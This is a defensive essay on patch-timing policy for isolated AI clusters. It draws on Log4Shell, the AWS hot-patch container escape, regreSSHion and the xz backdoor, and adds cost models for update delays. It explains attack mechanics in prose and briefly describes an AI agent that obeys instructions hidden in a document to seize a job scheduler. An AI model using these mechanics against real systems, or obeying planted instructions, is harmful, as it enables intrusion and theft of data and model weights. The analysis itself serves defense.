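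The Apache Software Foundation now lists these measures as discredited. They blocked the usual route from a message to a lookup but left others open. A program that called `Logger.printf("%s", userInput)` could still trigger a lookup, as could some programs with custom code for building messages. Neither setting stopped lookups in the logging configuration that used values supplied by users.

Deleting the `JndiLookup` class from the library file worked better, because Log4j can't perform a JNDI lookup without it. Apache still accepts this as an alternative to upgrading for the two most serious flaws, but an attacker can use other kinds of lookup to crash the program or copy private data into the logs.

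On a pinned cluster, deleting the class also changes the file's hash, so the team has to treat the edited file as a small backport and update the lockfile and gold image to match.

### Using the fast track more than once

The example cluster needs 48 hours for a fast-track review and 21 days for an ordinary update. The table assumes it was running Log4j 2.14.1 that December, configured so that the second and third flaws also affected it. Exposure starts on 9 December for Log4Shell and on the CVE date for the other two. The table omits the fourth flaw, which requires an attacker who can already change the logging configuration.

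| Approach | Installed | Fast-track reviews | Days exposed to Log4Shell | Flaw-days, first three flaws |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fast-track each of the first three releases | 12, 16 and 20 December | 3 | 3 | 7 |
| Wait for 2.17.0, then fast-track it | 20 December | 1 | 11 | 19 |
| Put 2.17.0 through the ordinary process | 8 January | 0 | 30 | 76 |
| Restart the ordinary process for every release, up to 2.17.1 | 18 January | 0 | 40 | 106 |

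The fast site's reviewers approved an incomplete fix, and the site had to declare a second emergency four days after the first. The slower sites installed better versions and did less work, but they were exposed to the worst flaw for much longer while attackers were scanning the whole internet for it. On 10 December nobody knew that two more releases would follow within eight days, so a team waiting for a settled version wouldn't have known when to stop.

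In the last row, every new release restarts the 14 days of staging, so no fix reaches production while fixes keep arriving less than 14 days apart. An operator could avoid this by letting the first release finish its review while the next one is in staging, or by moving the whole component to the fast track after the second fix.

A decent compromise for a team with few reviewers was to delete the `JndiLookup` class at once, which would block remote code execution, and then fast-track a single later release. The team could also leave 2.17.0 in the ordinary queue if it accepted the risk of a crash, since the third flaw, which that release fixed, doesn't let anyone steal data.

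### Finding the library

Finding the copies of Log4j was harder than replacing them, since replacing one library file takes minutes. A developer might install a search engine that contains a storage package that contains Log4j, without choosing Log4j or seeing its name. Java programs often come as a single archive with other archives inside, and some developers copy a library's code into their own package. A scanner that checks only the names of installed packages can miss Log4j in both cases.

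BestHub's *How Deep Is the Log4j Vulnerability in Maven Central?*, a repost of a December 2021 analysis, counts 35,863 packages in Maven's main repository that depended on vulnerable Log4j code on 16 December. That was more than 8% of the repository, and most of them depended on Log4j only indirectly. About five thousand had a fix by then. When a library is several levels down a dependency chain, each maintainer along the chain may have to wait for the maintainer below to publish a new version.

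The Cyber Safety Review Board spoke to groups representing organizations that already used software bills of materials, which list the components in a program. None reported using these lists to find vulnerable copies of Log4j, a problem the lists should have solved. The lists described components inconsistently and often left out version numbers. Apache couldn't help either, since it has no record of who uses its free software.

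A pinned cluster is easier to check because engineers can search its offline mirror instead of thousands of machines. They should open every archive, including archives inside archives, and look for the `JndiLookup` class. Searching for the name "log4j" would also turn up `log4j-api`, a companion file that doesn't have the flaw on its own.

The mirror won't show every copy of Log4j, because researchers may have built containers from other sources, and a vendor's management appliance can hold a copy that the operator has no permission to open. For those, engineers can submit a harmless lookup that points to their own server and see which machines try to contact it. A connection proves that a machine is vulnerable, but a machine that doesn't connect may still be vulnerable, because the test text may never have reached the part of the program that logs it.

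### Emergency Directive 22-02

CISA added Log4Shell to its KEV catalog on 10 December and issued an emergency directive to civilian agencies a week later. Crowell & Moring's *CISA Emergency Directive Requires Immediate Mitigation of Log4j Vulnerabilities* (2021), a law firm's summary, gives two deadlines:

- By 5 p.m. Eastern time on 23 December, agencies had to deal with the vulnerable software.
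- By 28 December, they had to report the affected applications to CISA.

The first deadline fell six days after the directive. By then, according to FCW's *CISA issues emergency directive to patch Log4j flaw* (2021), agencies had to list every system that accepted data from the internet, check its software against a list CISA kept on GitHub, and then patch it, apply one of CISA's mitigations or take it off the network. The board describes the period as two weeks, which is right only if counted from the disclosure on 9 December. Today's federal rules would allow three days for Log4Shell on an exposed server and require a forensic check.

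In the mitigation list published with *Emergency Directive 22-02*, CISA tells agencies to install the newest version of Log4j where they can and to treat anything else as temporary. A newer version came out the day after the directive, so an agency that had promptly installed 2.16.0 no longer had the newest one.

Agencies also had to assume that attackers had already broken into any affected system. Industrial Cyber's *CISA releases emergency directive to mitigate threats caused by Log4j vulnerabilities* reports that CISA told agencies to keep looking for signs of an intruder, such as outbound LDAP connections. This was sensible because exposed servers had been open to attack by anyone for a week.

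### What the response cost

One federal cabinet department told the Cyber Safety Review Board that it had spent 33,000 staff hours protecting its own networks from Log4j, equivalent to more than 16 people working full time for a year at 2,000 hours each. The board found that such efforts delayed other important work, including the response to other vulnerabilities. Its report doesn't show how many of the department's hours went to searching and how many to installing one release after another.

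The board published its review on 11 July 2022. It knew of no significant attack on critical infrastructure through Log4j, and it was somewhat surprised to find less exploitation than many experts had predicted. But it also mentioned several ransomware incidents between January and March 2022 and a wave of attacks on VMware Horizon servers that began on 19 January. A site that took 40 days to install the fix would have finished the day before that wave began.

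The evidence behind the finding is also weak, as the board acknowledged. Many organizations did not record whether attackers had used Log4j against them, and few had to report it. Defenders often couldn't tell an attacker's scan from a researcher's. An absence of reports is even less reassuring for a cluster that holds model weights. Unlike a ransomware gang, someone who copied the weights would have no reason to reveal it.

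Thousands of people spent that weekend patching servers and blocking traffic, and the board could not measure how many attacks they prevented. The low number of known attacks therefore does not show that the rush was unnecessary.

### Hot patches that opened containers

Amazon released hot patches to protect Java programs without restarting them. TechTarget's *AWS Log4Shell hot patch vulnerable to privilege escalation* dates the first to 12 December, two days after Log4j 2.15.0. A background service searched each machine for running Java programs and injected a correction into them. The service also worked outside Amazon's cloud, and from 17 December Amazon's version of Linux installed it automatically with its Java packages.

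*AWS's Log4Shell Hot Patch Vulnerable to Container Escape and Privilege Escalation* (Avrahami, 2022) describes a vulnerability that the service introduced. The service looked for any program named "java", including inside containers. When it found one in a container, it ran the container's own "java" file twice, first to learn the version and then to apply the patch. It ran the file as root and without most of the limits normally placed on containers. An attacker could name a malicious program "java", wait for the service to run it, and then take over the host.

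Amazon's hot patch for Log4Shell let any container on a machine take control of that machine, even if the container didn't run Java. Unprivileged programs outside containers could also exploit the patch to gain full control. Researchers at the security company Palo Alto Networks noticed the problem on 20 December, six days after Amazon released a version of the patch for containers. Amazon published fixes on 23 December, but the researchers had found ways around them by 27 December. Amazon released the final fixes on 19 April 2022, though Debian and Ubuntu users had to wait until early May for one of them.

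For an ordinary company with web servers on the internet, the hot patch was probably still worth installing in December. Log4Shell let any stranger in, while the patch's own flaws were useful only to an attacker who could already run something on the machine. Avrahami advised anyone still patching Log4Shell to finish that first. Strangers can't reach an isolated research cluster, but researchers and AI agents start containers there all day, so a service that lets any container take over its host could easily do more harm than the flaw it fixes.

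The operators of such a cluster should review a hot patch like any other emergency software, checking in particular what privileges it needs, and remove it once they have upgraded the library. Avrahami suspected that many users left the patch running as an extra precaution. Anyone who installed the container version on 14 December and forgot about it was exposed for 126 days to a known or undiscovered flaw that allowed escape from every container, although a safe version of Log4j had been available for most of that time.

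### What blocking outbound traffic would have stopped

The standard Log4Shell attack needs the vulnerable machine to open a connection to the attacker's server. If a firewall blocks that connection, Log4j can't load the attacker's code. Many security engineers relied on this in December 2021, and an isolated cluster already blocks such connections before anyone discloses the flaw. But only some of the kinds of attack that the four CVEs allow need a connection outside the cluster.

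| Attack | Would a block at the cluster's edge stop it? |
|---|---|
| Load code from a server on the internet | Yes |
| Load code from a server that the attacker runs inside the cluster | No |
| Use a lookup to copy private data into the logs | No |
| Crash the program with a lookup that refers to itself | No |
| Change the logging configuration to load remote code | Only if the code is on an outside server |

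The second row is the most serious case. A researcher with a grudge, or an AI agent following instructions hidden in a document, could start a small directory server in a container and submit a job whose name contains the lookup. If the job scheduler logs the name with a vulnerable Log4j, it will contact that container and run whatever it receives. The attacker then controls the scheduler, which can usually start programs on every node. Stopping this requires firewall rules between machines inside the cluster that let the scheduler connect only to the servers it needs.

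In the third row, the attacker needs to be able to read the logs. A lookup can insert the value of an environment variable into the log, and programs often keep passwords in environment variables. On many clusters, researchers can read the logs of their own jobs and sometimes those of shared services. Firewalls won't detect this, because the program only writes to its usual log.

An outsider can still get malicious text into an isolated cluster, for instance in the name of a file in a training set. If the cluster has no route out and the outsider has no help inside, the text could crash a service or put a password in a log that the outsider can't read, but it couldn't fetch a program from the internet. The air gap would therefore have been a good reason to patch the job scheduler before a log server that handles only imported data, but it wouldn't have justified leaving the scheduler until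 January.

The block also helps with detection. A log server on an isolated network has no legitimate reason to contact an outside directory server. If the firewall records even one attempt, a vulnerable copy of Log4j has probably processed hostile text, and the operators should trace that text to its source.

### Five years later

*BO Team Used Log4Shell to Breach a Russian Developer* (Reyes, 2026) reported in November 2026 that, according to the security company Kaspersky, attackers had used Log4Shell against a Russian software developer. They got in through an unpatched copy of vCenter, VMware's tool for managing virtual machines, and reached the server that signs the developer's software. Control of that server would let them sign malicious updates, so a company that patches everything can still suffer a supply chain attack if its supplier leaves a known flaw unpatched.

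The board expected vulnerable copies of Log4j to remain in use for a decade or longer, and download figures so far support that expectation. When the flaw became public, more than 99% of downloads were vulnerable. Sonatype's *Exploring Unnecessary Risk* puts the share for 2025 at roughly 13%, or about 40 million of nearly 300 million downloads. Woollacott's *One-in-ten log4j-core downloads are still vulnerable* (2026) reports newer Sonatype data, apparently for a single month, in which 2.49 million of almost 24.3 million downloads (10.3%) were vulnerable. The share for 2026 as a whole was nearly 12%.

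Download counts don't reliably show how many vulnerable programs are running. An automated build may download the same old version hundreds of times a day, while a program installed in 2020 adds nothing to the count. The best figures on applications are older. IT Pro's *What is the Log4Shell vulnerability?* cites a December 2023 report by the security company Veracode, in which 2.8% of applications used a version with the original flaw. Another 3.8% used 2.17.0, which has only the fourth, much less dangerous flaw, and 32% used the unsupported 1.x series. IT Pro describes all 38,000 applications in the report as vulnerable, but the percentages make sense only if that was the number examined. If so, about 1,100 still had Log4Shell two years after the fix.

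Old version pins probably account for some of the vulnerable downloads, though isolated clusters barely appear in these statistics. Their operators can delete the vulnerable versions from the mirror so that any build that still needs one fails visibly. They also have to search old container images and backups, because deleting versions from the mirror won't reveal any copies already stored there.

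## The OpenSSH flaw and the xz backdoor of 2024

Two events in 2024 threatened sshd, OpenSSH's remote-login server. In March, a developer discovered that somebody had put a backdoor into xz, a compression package whose library sshd loads on some Linux distributions. The sites that had it were those that installed new releases quickly. In July, OpenSSH's developers fixed regreSSHion (CVE-2024-6387), a flaw that could let an attacker take over a server without a password, and sites that delayed the update remained at risk.

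### A race against the login timer

A client that connects to sshd normally has 120 seconds to log in. If the time runs out, the operating system interrupts sshd, whatever it is doing, and runs a short routine that logs the timeout and closes the connection. The security company Qualys found the flaw in this routine and explained it in *regreSSHion* (2024).

The routine calls `syslog()`, the standard logging function. On Linux systems that use glibc, the most common C library, `syslog()` allocates and frees memory. If the timer interrupts sshd during a memory allocation, sshd's records of free memory are briefly wrong when `syslog()` uses them. An attacker who has already filled parts of that memory with carefully chosen data can make sshd run their code. The code runs as root because this part of sshd has full privileges and no sandbox.

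The attack is hard to time. Qualys's researchers sent sshd all but the last byte of a large public key early, then sent the last byte just before the deadline, so that sshd would be reading the key when the timer went off. They arranged the memory to give each attempt 27 chances to succeed, but still needed about 10,000 attempts on average.

Mark Dowd reported the same mistake in OpenSSH in 2006, and the developers fixed it in version 4.4 by adding a condition that excluded the unsafe logging from the routine. In October 2020 a developer reorganizing the logging code accidentally deleted that condition, and the flaw returned in version 8.5p1.

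| OpenSSH version | Exposure to regreSSHion on Linux with glibc |
|---|---|
| Before 4.4p1 | Vulnerable, unless someone has backported a correct fix for the 2006 flaw |
| 4.4p1 to 8.4p1 | Not vulnerable |
| 8.5p1 to 9.7p1 | Vulnerable |
| 9.8p1 | Fixed |

Clusters pinned to Red Hat Enterprise Linux 8, which uses OpenSSH 8.0p1, never had the OpenSSH flaw, but clusters that had moved to version 9, which uses OpenSSH 8.7p1, did. Staying on older pinned software gave no such advantage with Log4Shell.

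Attackers could also have found regreSSHion before it was announced. The fix went into OpenSSH's public repository on 6 June, 25 days before the announcement. It was part of a large change whose title mentioned only penalties for badly behaved clients, so a casual reader would probably have missed it. Somebody had also filed a public bug report about sshd freezing in the same routine. When Qualys's researchers saw that report, they stopped work on a better exploit and contacted the developers immediately.

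### How long an attack takes

By default, sshd allows up to 100 unfinished logins at a time, and in this attack each one lasts the full 120 seconds. For 10,000 attempts, that gives:

$$\frac{10{,}000}{100}\times 120\ \text{s}=12{,}000\ \text{s}\approx 3.3\ \text{hours}$$

The attacker also has to guess where glibc is in memory, because Linux randomizes its address. On the 32-bit version of Debian 12 that Qualys tested, the guess was right about half the time, so a successful attack took six to eight hours on average. The researchers attacked virtual machines over a mostly stable network link. They expected that they could improve the method.

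Nearly all AI clusters run 64-bit systems, which have many more possible addresses. When Qualys published, its researchers had started but not finished a 64-bit exploit for Rocky Linux 9, a free rebuild of Red Hat's distribution. They hoped to reduce the attack time to less than a week. According to the OpenSSH (2024) release notes, the developers also believed a 64-bit attack was possible but knew of no demonstration.

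No one seems to have publicly demonstrated a reliable 64-bit attack yet. Trend Micro's *The Potential Impact of the OpenSSH Vulnerabilities CVE-2024–6387 and CVE-2024-6409* called such an attack "highly impractical" and reported no change in the security company's own attack data. The strongest claim to the contrary comes from KEVIntel, a tracker that listed the flaw in October 2025 as successfully exploited, with 70% confidence. GCVE's *CVE-2024-6387* (2024), a database record that includes this claim, gives no details of the attack and notes that the flaw was not in CISA's KEV catalog.

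The OpenSSH flaw was judged hard to exploit in 2024 based on people's skill and patience, and AI has weakened that judgment. Calif's *Claude Wrote a Full FreeBSD Remote Kernel RCE with Root Shell* describes how Anthropic's model Claude turned a published FreeBSD flaw into a working remote attack in about eight hours in March 2026. Anthropic also reports that its Mythos Preview model has exploited subtle race conditions on Linux and bypassed the randomization of kernel addresses. In those cases the attacker could already run programs on the machine, which makes the timing easier than over a network. Even so, an operator who left the OpenSSH flaw unpatched in 2024 because nobody could exploit it should not rely on that reasoning today.

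Trend Micro also passes on a warning that fake regreSSHion exploits installed malware on the computers of security researchers who ran them. A team should therefore run such code only on an isolated spare machine.

Qualys reported in *Remote Unauthenticated Code Execution Vulnerability in OpenSSH Server (regreSSHion)* (2024) that internet search services showed more than 14 million potentially vulnerable servers. Among Qualys's customers, about 700,000 internet-facing servers were vulnerable, or 31% of those running OpenSSH. The larger figure presumably relies on the version number each server announces, so it would include 64-bit machines that nobody knew how to attack.

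It would also include servers that a distribution had accidentally made safe. Ubuntu 24.04 had changed how sshd starts, with the side effect that memory addresses no longer changed with each connection. OpenSSH's developers warned that this might make an attack easier. But Qualys found that the same change kept the logging function from allocating memory inside the timeout routine, so this attack did not work on Ubuntu 24.04.

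On 2 July 2024, CISA assessed that the OpenSSH flaw had a public proof of concept, was not automatable and had total impact. Under the 2026 federal deadlines, a flaw with those ratings would have to be patched within 14 days on a gateway on the public internet, and by the next upgrade on an internal one. Under the stricter definitions of exposure and automation suggested earlier, both gateways would have to be patched within three days.

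### Turning off the timer

Administrators who couldn't update could set `LoginGraceTime` to 0 in sshd's configuration file. This turns off the timer, so the unsafe routine never runs and the attack can't work. But a client that never logs in can then stay connected indefinitely, and once 100 such clients are connected, sshd refuses all new connections. Miller warned of this when he announced the release.

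Suppose researchers reach a cluster through three login gateways. With the timer off, an attacker could block all new logins by opening 300 connections and leaving them idle. This attack was already possible with the timer on, but the attacker had to replace all 300 connections every two minutes. Without the timer, a faulty monitoring script could also block logins by accident if it opens connections and never closes them. People who are already logged in can keep working.

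The lockout also affects the people who must install the fix, if they use the same gateways. Before changing the setting, operators need a second way in, such as a physical console or a separate management network. They should also let only known addresses connect to the gateways and watch the number of unfinished logins.

Trend Micro's advice to reduce the login time is misleading, because only setting it to 0 removes the flaw. A shorter time lets the attacker make more attempts per hour. At 20 seconds instead of 120, the 10,000 attempts in the calculation above would take 33 minutes. Allowing fewer unfinished logins slows the attack, but it makes it easier to lock users out.

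For most clusters with a handful of gateways, the trade is worthwhile. A lockout is obvious within minutes and loses people some working time, while an attacker with root access to a gateway can capture researchers' credentials and use them to get further into the cluster. The training nodes need the setting too, because they often run sshd, and an AI agent or someone using a researcher's stolen account may be able to reach them without using a gateway.

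The attack is easy to detect in the logs of an unpatched sshd. At 100 attempts every two minutes, the server would record about 3,000 login timeouts an hour, far more than researchers cause in normal use. However, both quick remedies remove these log entries. Turning off the login timer prevents timeouts, and the two-line patch that Miller posted works by omitting the logging code. Teams that apply either remedy have to count connections at the firewall to detect further attempts.

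Operators whose researchers share one address can exempt it from the login penalties in the full 9.8 release. But an attacker on one of the researchers' machines would then be exempt too, so it is better to let the gateways tell users' machines apart.

### A second flaw a week later

While reviewing Qualys's findings, the security researcher Solar Designer (2024) found a related flaw, CVE-2024-6409, in OpenSSH 8.7 and 8.8. It seems to be harmless in the versions that OpenSSH's developers released. But because of a patch Red Hat added for audit logging, a second process that handles clients before they log in also frees memory when the timer runs out. The flaw affected Red Hat Enterprise Linux 9, its rebuilds, and Fedora 36 and 37, both already out of support.

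An attacker would gain less from this flaw because the process has few privileges. Nobody had tried to exploit it when Solar Designer disclosed it. Rocky Linux's fix changed a single line.

Distributions knew about both flaws before either became public. Solar Designer reported the second to them on 26 June, but Red Hat was already preparing its fix for the first and wasn't ready to add another, so the second flaw wasn't disclosed until 8 July, a week after the first. Solar Designer apologized for the separate disclosures and wrote that a joint one would have saved many people time.

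Clusters that fast-tracked the first fix on Red Hat Enterprise Linux 9 or a rebuild of it had to repeat the work a week later, as the early Log4j patchers did. The fixes took longer to reach all of Red Hat's products. *CVE-2024-6387 openssh* (Benatto, 2024) shows that Red Hat was still issuing fixes for regreSSHion on 18 July. For the second flaw, another tracker entry by Benatto (2024) shows the first fix on 10 July and more until 22 August.

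Setting `LoginGraceTime` to 0 turns off the timer and protects against both flaws. Some administrators had instead started sshd with the `-e` option, which redirects log messages, but this fully protects only against the first flaw. An operator who turned off the timer on 1 July could have waited for the second fix and reviewed both fixes together.

### The xz backdoor

The attacker put malicious code into xz versions 5.6.0 and 5.6.1, released in late February and on 9 March 2024 respectively, according to Hackaday's *Security Alert* (2024). The developer Andres Freund discovered it because SSH logins on Debian's development branch were using too much processor time. A login attempt that should have failed in 0.3 seconds took 0.8. Freund published his analysis, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (2024), on 29 March, nearly five weeks after the first compromised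 release.

Most of the backdoor's code was in the project's public repository, disguised as two compressed test files. The line that started unpacking them was only in the release archives, the packaged copies of the source that distributions download. Someone reading the repository would therefore have seen only two unused test files.

When a distribution built the xz package, a hidden script checked whether it was running on 64-bit Intel or AMD Linux, with the GNU compiler and linker, as part of a Debian or RPM package build. If so, it inserted the backdoor into liblzma, the library that other programs use to read xz files.

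OpenSSH doesn't use liblzma, but Debian and several other distributions had patched sshd to notify systemd, the service manager, when it was ready. The patched sshd loaded a systemd library, which loaded liblzma. *Wolves in the Repository* (2025) points out that the distributions had created the dependency the attacker needed.

Once inside sshd, the backdoor took over a function that checks signatures during login. An attacker with one particular private key could then hide a command in the certificate a client presents, and the server would run it before the login was complete, according to *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (2024). Ordinary criminals scanning the internet could not have used the backdoor without that key. On an isolated cluster, the attacker would also have needed an accomplice or a stolen account inside to reach sshd.

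Freund wrote that few distributions had adopted the backdoored versions, most of them only in pre-release branches. Linux Compatible lists security notices for Debian's testing branch, Fedora 40 and Rawhide, Kali, Arch and Gentoo. Arch and Gentoo build neither Debian nor RPM packages, so the script that Freund analysed should not have altered their copies of liblzma, although they distributed the backdoored source.

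Clusters pinned to an older xz avoided all this without doing anything, as did those following a stable distribution that had not yet picked up version 5.6. Sites that had installed the new version had to return to an older one. In the discussion of Freund's message, Liguori (2024) warned against downloading even older archives from the project's website, because the attacker had access to the signing key and could have altered them. An operator with an offline mirror could instead use the copy stored there, after checking it against the hash in an old lockfile.

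An internal build system might not have protected the sites that did take the new version. If it built an RPM package from the release archive, it would have compiled the backdoor and signed the result with the organization's own key. Building from the repository would have avoided the backdoor, because the repository lacked the line that unpacked the code. Comparing the archive with the repository would have revealed that line, but reviewers could easily have dismissed the difference, because release archives usually contain generated build files that a repository lacks.

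OpenSSH 9.8 made both problems less likely for its own users. The developers now keep the generated files in the repository's release branch, so the branch should match the release archive exactly. They also added systemd notification that doesn't need the systemd library, so distributions no longer have to patch in that feature themselves. A cluster that applied only the two-line patch in July got neither change, which is a good reason to schedule the full upgrade later through the ordinary process.

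### Three sites through both events

The first of three hypothetical sites installs every release on the day it appears. The second waits 30 days. The third also waits 30 days but uses an emergency lane to install urgent fixes in 48 hours.

All three take xz and OpenSSH from the original projects, build them in a way that triggers the backdoor, and run an affected version of OpenSSH on 1 July. Their reviewers don't notice the backdoor, and all three remove it on the day Freund publishes. The table uses 24 February as the release date of xz 5.6.0, counts exposure to regreSSHion from the day the flaw was disclosed, and assumes that nobody turns off the login timer.

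| Site | Installs xz 5.6.0 | Days with the backdoor | Fixes regreSSHion | Days exposed to regreSSHion |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Always updates | 24 February | 34 | 1 July | 0 |
| 30-day delay | 25 March | 4 | 31 July | 30 |
| 30-day delay and emergency lane | 25 March | 4 | 3 July | 2 |

The 30-day delay was slightly too short to keep the backdoor out. Sites that waited 35 days would have avoided it, while a cluster that took 21 days to install each update would have run it for 13 days. The result also depends on whether a site restarts the wait when a newer release replaces the pending one. A site that did so would have discarded 5.6.0 on 9 March and never installed 5.6.1. In December 2021, restarting the wait produced the longest exposure to Log4Shell.

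The emergency lane gets the OpenSSH fix installed 28 days sooner in July. It does no harm in March, because the xz releases didn't claim to fix an urgent security flaw. If the attacker had announced 5.6.1 as an urgent security fix, the third site might have fast-tracked it and had the backdoor for 18 days.

The second site could have done nearly as well as the third by turning off the login timer on 1 July. An operator with few reviewers can therefore get much of the benefit of an emergency lane by being able to change one setting quickly.

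Real sites that depend on a distribution also have to wait for it to package the fix. AlmaLinux's *Important* (2024) gives 3 July as the date of the regreSSHion fix for AlmaLinux 9, another rebuild of Red Hat's distribution, so even a site that always updated would have been exposed for two days. A cluster on Red Hat Enterprise Linux 8 would have had zeros in both columns even without an emergency lane.

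### Why two cases cannot settle the policy

The first two sites each happen to have 34 days of exposure in total, but adding the days makes little sense because they are not equally dangerous. The backdoor gave one attacker a reliable way in for 34 days. Anyone could try to exploit regreSSHion during its 30 days, but nobody is known to have had a working attack on a 64-bit system. An operator who fears a state agency would probably give the backdoor more weight, while one who fears criminals scanning the internet would have more reason to worry about flaws like regreSSHion.

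The figures also depend on luck. Freund noticed the xz backdoor because of a half-second delay. A better-written backdoor might have gone unnoticed for a year, and waiting 30 days would then have achieved very little. If regreSSHion had been as easy to exploit as Log4Shell, waiting 30 days to patch it could have been disastrous, and even two days might have been too long.

Waiting also worked in March only because other people installed the new version sooner. Freund found the backdoor on a system that already had that version, and if every site had waited 30 days, the backdoor might have stayed hidden longer.

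The OpenSSH flaw and the xz backdoor are well known because they were unusual. Most releases contain neither a backdoor nor an urgent fix, so a fair comparison would have to count how often each occurs. Urgent fixes are not rare. ThreatCluster's *CVE-2024-6387* mentions another critical OpenSSH release, on 5 November 2026, apparently for a flaw that let attackers bypass password checks on Alpine Linux. Backdoored releases are harder to count because a successful backdoor may never be discovered.

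## Weighing exposure to known flaws against poisoned updates

Log4Shell, regreSSHion and the xz backdoor show how much harm a delay caused or prevented in three cases. To set a waiting period that will apply to years of releases, an operator has to estimate how often urgent flaws and poisoned releases appear and how much damage each does. *Dependency cooldowns considered harmful*, the essay that described the clash between cooldowns and flaw auditors, also puts such estimates into a simple cost model.

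### What a longer delay costs and saves

The model adds an annual cost from known flaws to an annual cost from poisoned updates:

$$\text{Annual cost}=\lambda\,d\,c_{\text{flaw}}+r\,P\,c_{\text{comp}}$$

λ is the number of flaws disclosed each year in the software a site runs, d is the number of days each fix waits, and c_flaw is the cost of leaving one flaw unpatched for one day. For poisoned updates, r is the number of poisoned releases each year among packages the site might install, P is the chance that the site installs one before anybody detects it, and c_comp is the cost of the resulting compromise.

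The essay's example is a Python service with 25 flaws and 0.1 poisoned releases a year. A team that installs every fix within a day has 25 flaw-days a year. An 8-day cooldown raises that to 200, so it adds 175 flaw-days. In return, the chance of installing a poisoned release before anyone detects it falls from 34% to 20%. Since only one such release appears every ten years, the cooldown prevents about one compromise every 69 years. It pays only if a compromise costs more than this many flaw-days:

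$$\frac{175}{0.1\times(0.341-0.196)}\approx 12{,}000$$

The chance of detection comes from an assumed curve. The essay supposes that half of all poisoned releases last half a day on average, 30% last three days and 20% last sixty days. The chance that a release is still undetected t days after publication is then:

$$P(t)=0.5\,e^{-2t}+0.3\,e^{-t/3}+0.2\,e^{-t/60}$$

The best delay depends on what a compromise would cost:

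| Cost of one compromise, in flaw-days | Best delay in the essay | Kind of service |
|---|---|---|
| 100 to 10,000 | 1 day | Ordinary web services and internal tools |
| 100,000 | 14 days | Financial technology, identity services |
| 1,000,000 | 90 days | Payments, cryptocurrency custody, critical infrastructure |

A one-day delay adds no risk in this model because the team takes a day to notice a flaw anyway. A cluster that holds frontier model weights presumably belongs in one of the lower rows, where long delays are the better choice.

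The table looks more precise than it is. If a compromise does as much harm as 100,000 flaw-days, the formula gives a total annual harm of 1,962 flaw-days for a 14-day delay, 1,937 for 21 days and 1,963 for 30 days, so an operator could pick any of the three. At a million flaw-days, the annual total keeps falling until the delay reaches about 155 days. The essay presumably stopped at 90 because no longer delay was tested.

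The essay describes all its inputs as guesses and estimates that the break-even point could be anywhere from 6,000 to 30,000 flaw-days. The rate of poisoned releases matters most, since a tenfold increase would cut the break-even point to about 1,200 flaw-days.

Data from npm allow a rough check on that rate. *A Difference Without a Distinction* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) counts 1,654 established npm packages that attackers poisoned between April 2023 and September 2026, or about 470 a year. *Pinning Is Futile* (He, Vasilescu and Kästner, 2025) reports that the registry held more than three million packages in 2024. A cluster using 500 randomly chosen packages would therefore encounter about 0.08 poisoned ones a year, which is surprisingly close to the essay's guess.

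But nobody chooses packages at random, and attackers prefer popular ones. Attackers targeted LiteLLM, a library that lets programs call many different AI models, in March 2026. *LiteLLM Compromised in Fresh Supply Chain Attack* (Arghire, 2026) reports that in October, attackers used stolen access tokens to push and approve malicious versions again. A cluster that used LiteLLM would have faced two poisonings in a year from that library alone.

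### Adding an emergency lane

The 175 extra flaw-days arise only because the essay's cooldown delays security fixes along with all other updates. The figures below use invented inputs to illustrate what an emergency lane changes.

Suppose that 2 of the 25 flaws each year are dangerous, meaning that attackers exploit them and can reach them in this cluster. If every fix waits 30 days, the two dangerous flaws add up to 60 flaw-days a year. The operators then add a lane that installs urgent fixes in 2 days, and their triage recognizes 80% of the dangerous flaws. The expected total falls to:

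$$2\times(0.8\times 2+0.2\times 30)=3.2+12=15.2$$

The lane removes three quarters of the dangerous flaw-days. Of the 15.2 that remain, 12 come from flaws that the team failed to recognize and left in the ordinary queue. This makes better triage worth more than a faster lane:

| Change to the example | Dangerous flaw-days a year |
|---|---|
| None | 15.2 |
| Cut the lane from 2 days to 1 | 13.6 |
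| Recognize 90% of dangerous flaws instead of 80% | 9.6 |
| Cut the ordinary delay from 30 days to 14 | 8.8 |

A team that already patches urgent flaws in two days should therefore improve its triage before trying to reach one day. It should recheck the flaws in the ordinary queue every day, since the second Log4j flaw looked minor when it first appeared. Shortening the ordinary delay helps most in this example, but it also raises the chance that a poisoned release is still undetected at installation from 12% to 16%.

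### If attackers aim for the fast lane

Under the essay's curve, a poisoned release has a 0.36 probability of still being undetected at day 2 and 0.12 at day 30. This difference hardly matters if attackers don't target the fast lane, because a cluster that installs 1,000 updates a year and fast-tracks five of them would put only one poisoned release in 200 through it. But an attacker who always disguises the release as an urgent fix would succeed almost three times as often as one whose release has to wait 30 days.

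An operator needs a common unit to compare that risk with the dangerous flaw-days. For a cluster that holds model weights, the unit can be expected thefts, because both risks can end in somebody stealing the weights. Converting flaw-days to thefts requires an estimate of the daily chance that somebody steals the weights through a dangerous flaw. The next table shows expected thefts per 1,000 years for three guesses at that chance. It assumes that every poisoned release the cluster installs leads to a theft and that reviewers catch none of them, which is too pessimistic but treats all the policies alike.

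| Daily chance of theft through a dangerous flaw | Everything after 2 days | Everything after 30 days | Two lanes, attackers ignore the fast one | Two lanes, attackers always use the fast one |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100 | 76 | 612 | 164 | 188 |
| 1 in 1,000 | 40 | 72 | 27 | 51 |
| 1 in 10,000 | 36 | 18 | 14 | 37 |

The top row might suit a login gateway on the internet, where attackers would soon use any dangerous flaw. Even the 20% of flaws that triage misses would do so much harm there in 30 days that installing everything quickly is better. The bottom row is closer to a well-isolated cluster. A long delay for all updates is better than a short one only if the daily chance is below about 1 in 2,400.

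Using two lanes gives the best results in the lower two rows as long as attackers don't use the emergency lane. If they always use it, the cluster is as exposed to poisoned updates as a site that installs everything after two days, but has almost four times as many dangerous flaw-days. The benefit of an emergency lane therefore depends on how well its updates are reviewed. If the ordinary lane relied on waiting alone, reviewers in the emergency lane would have to catch about two thirds of the poisoned releases still undetected on day 2 to make both lanes equally safe.

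Automatic checks on how a release was published won't reliably catch poisoned updates. The package manager pnpm has an optional policy that refuses a release if it carries weaker evidence of its origin than an earlier release did, for example because somebody uploaded it by hand instead of through the project's automated build. Santos-Grueiro replayed the policy on 41 malicious releases from 12 attacks that used stolen credentials. The policy flagged 17, and the attackers could have got 15 of those past it by adding evidence of origin.

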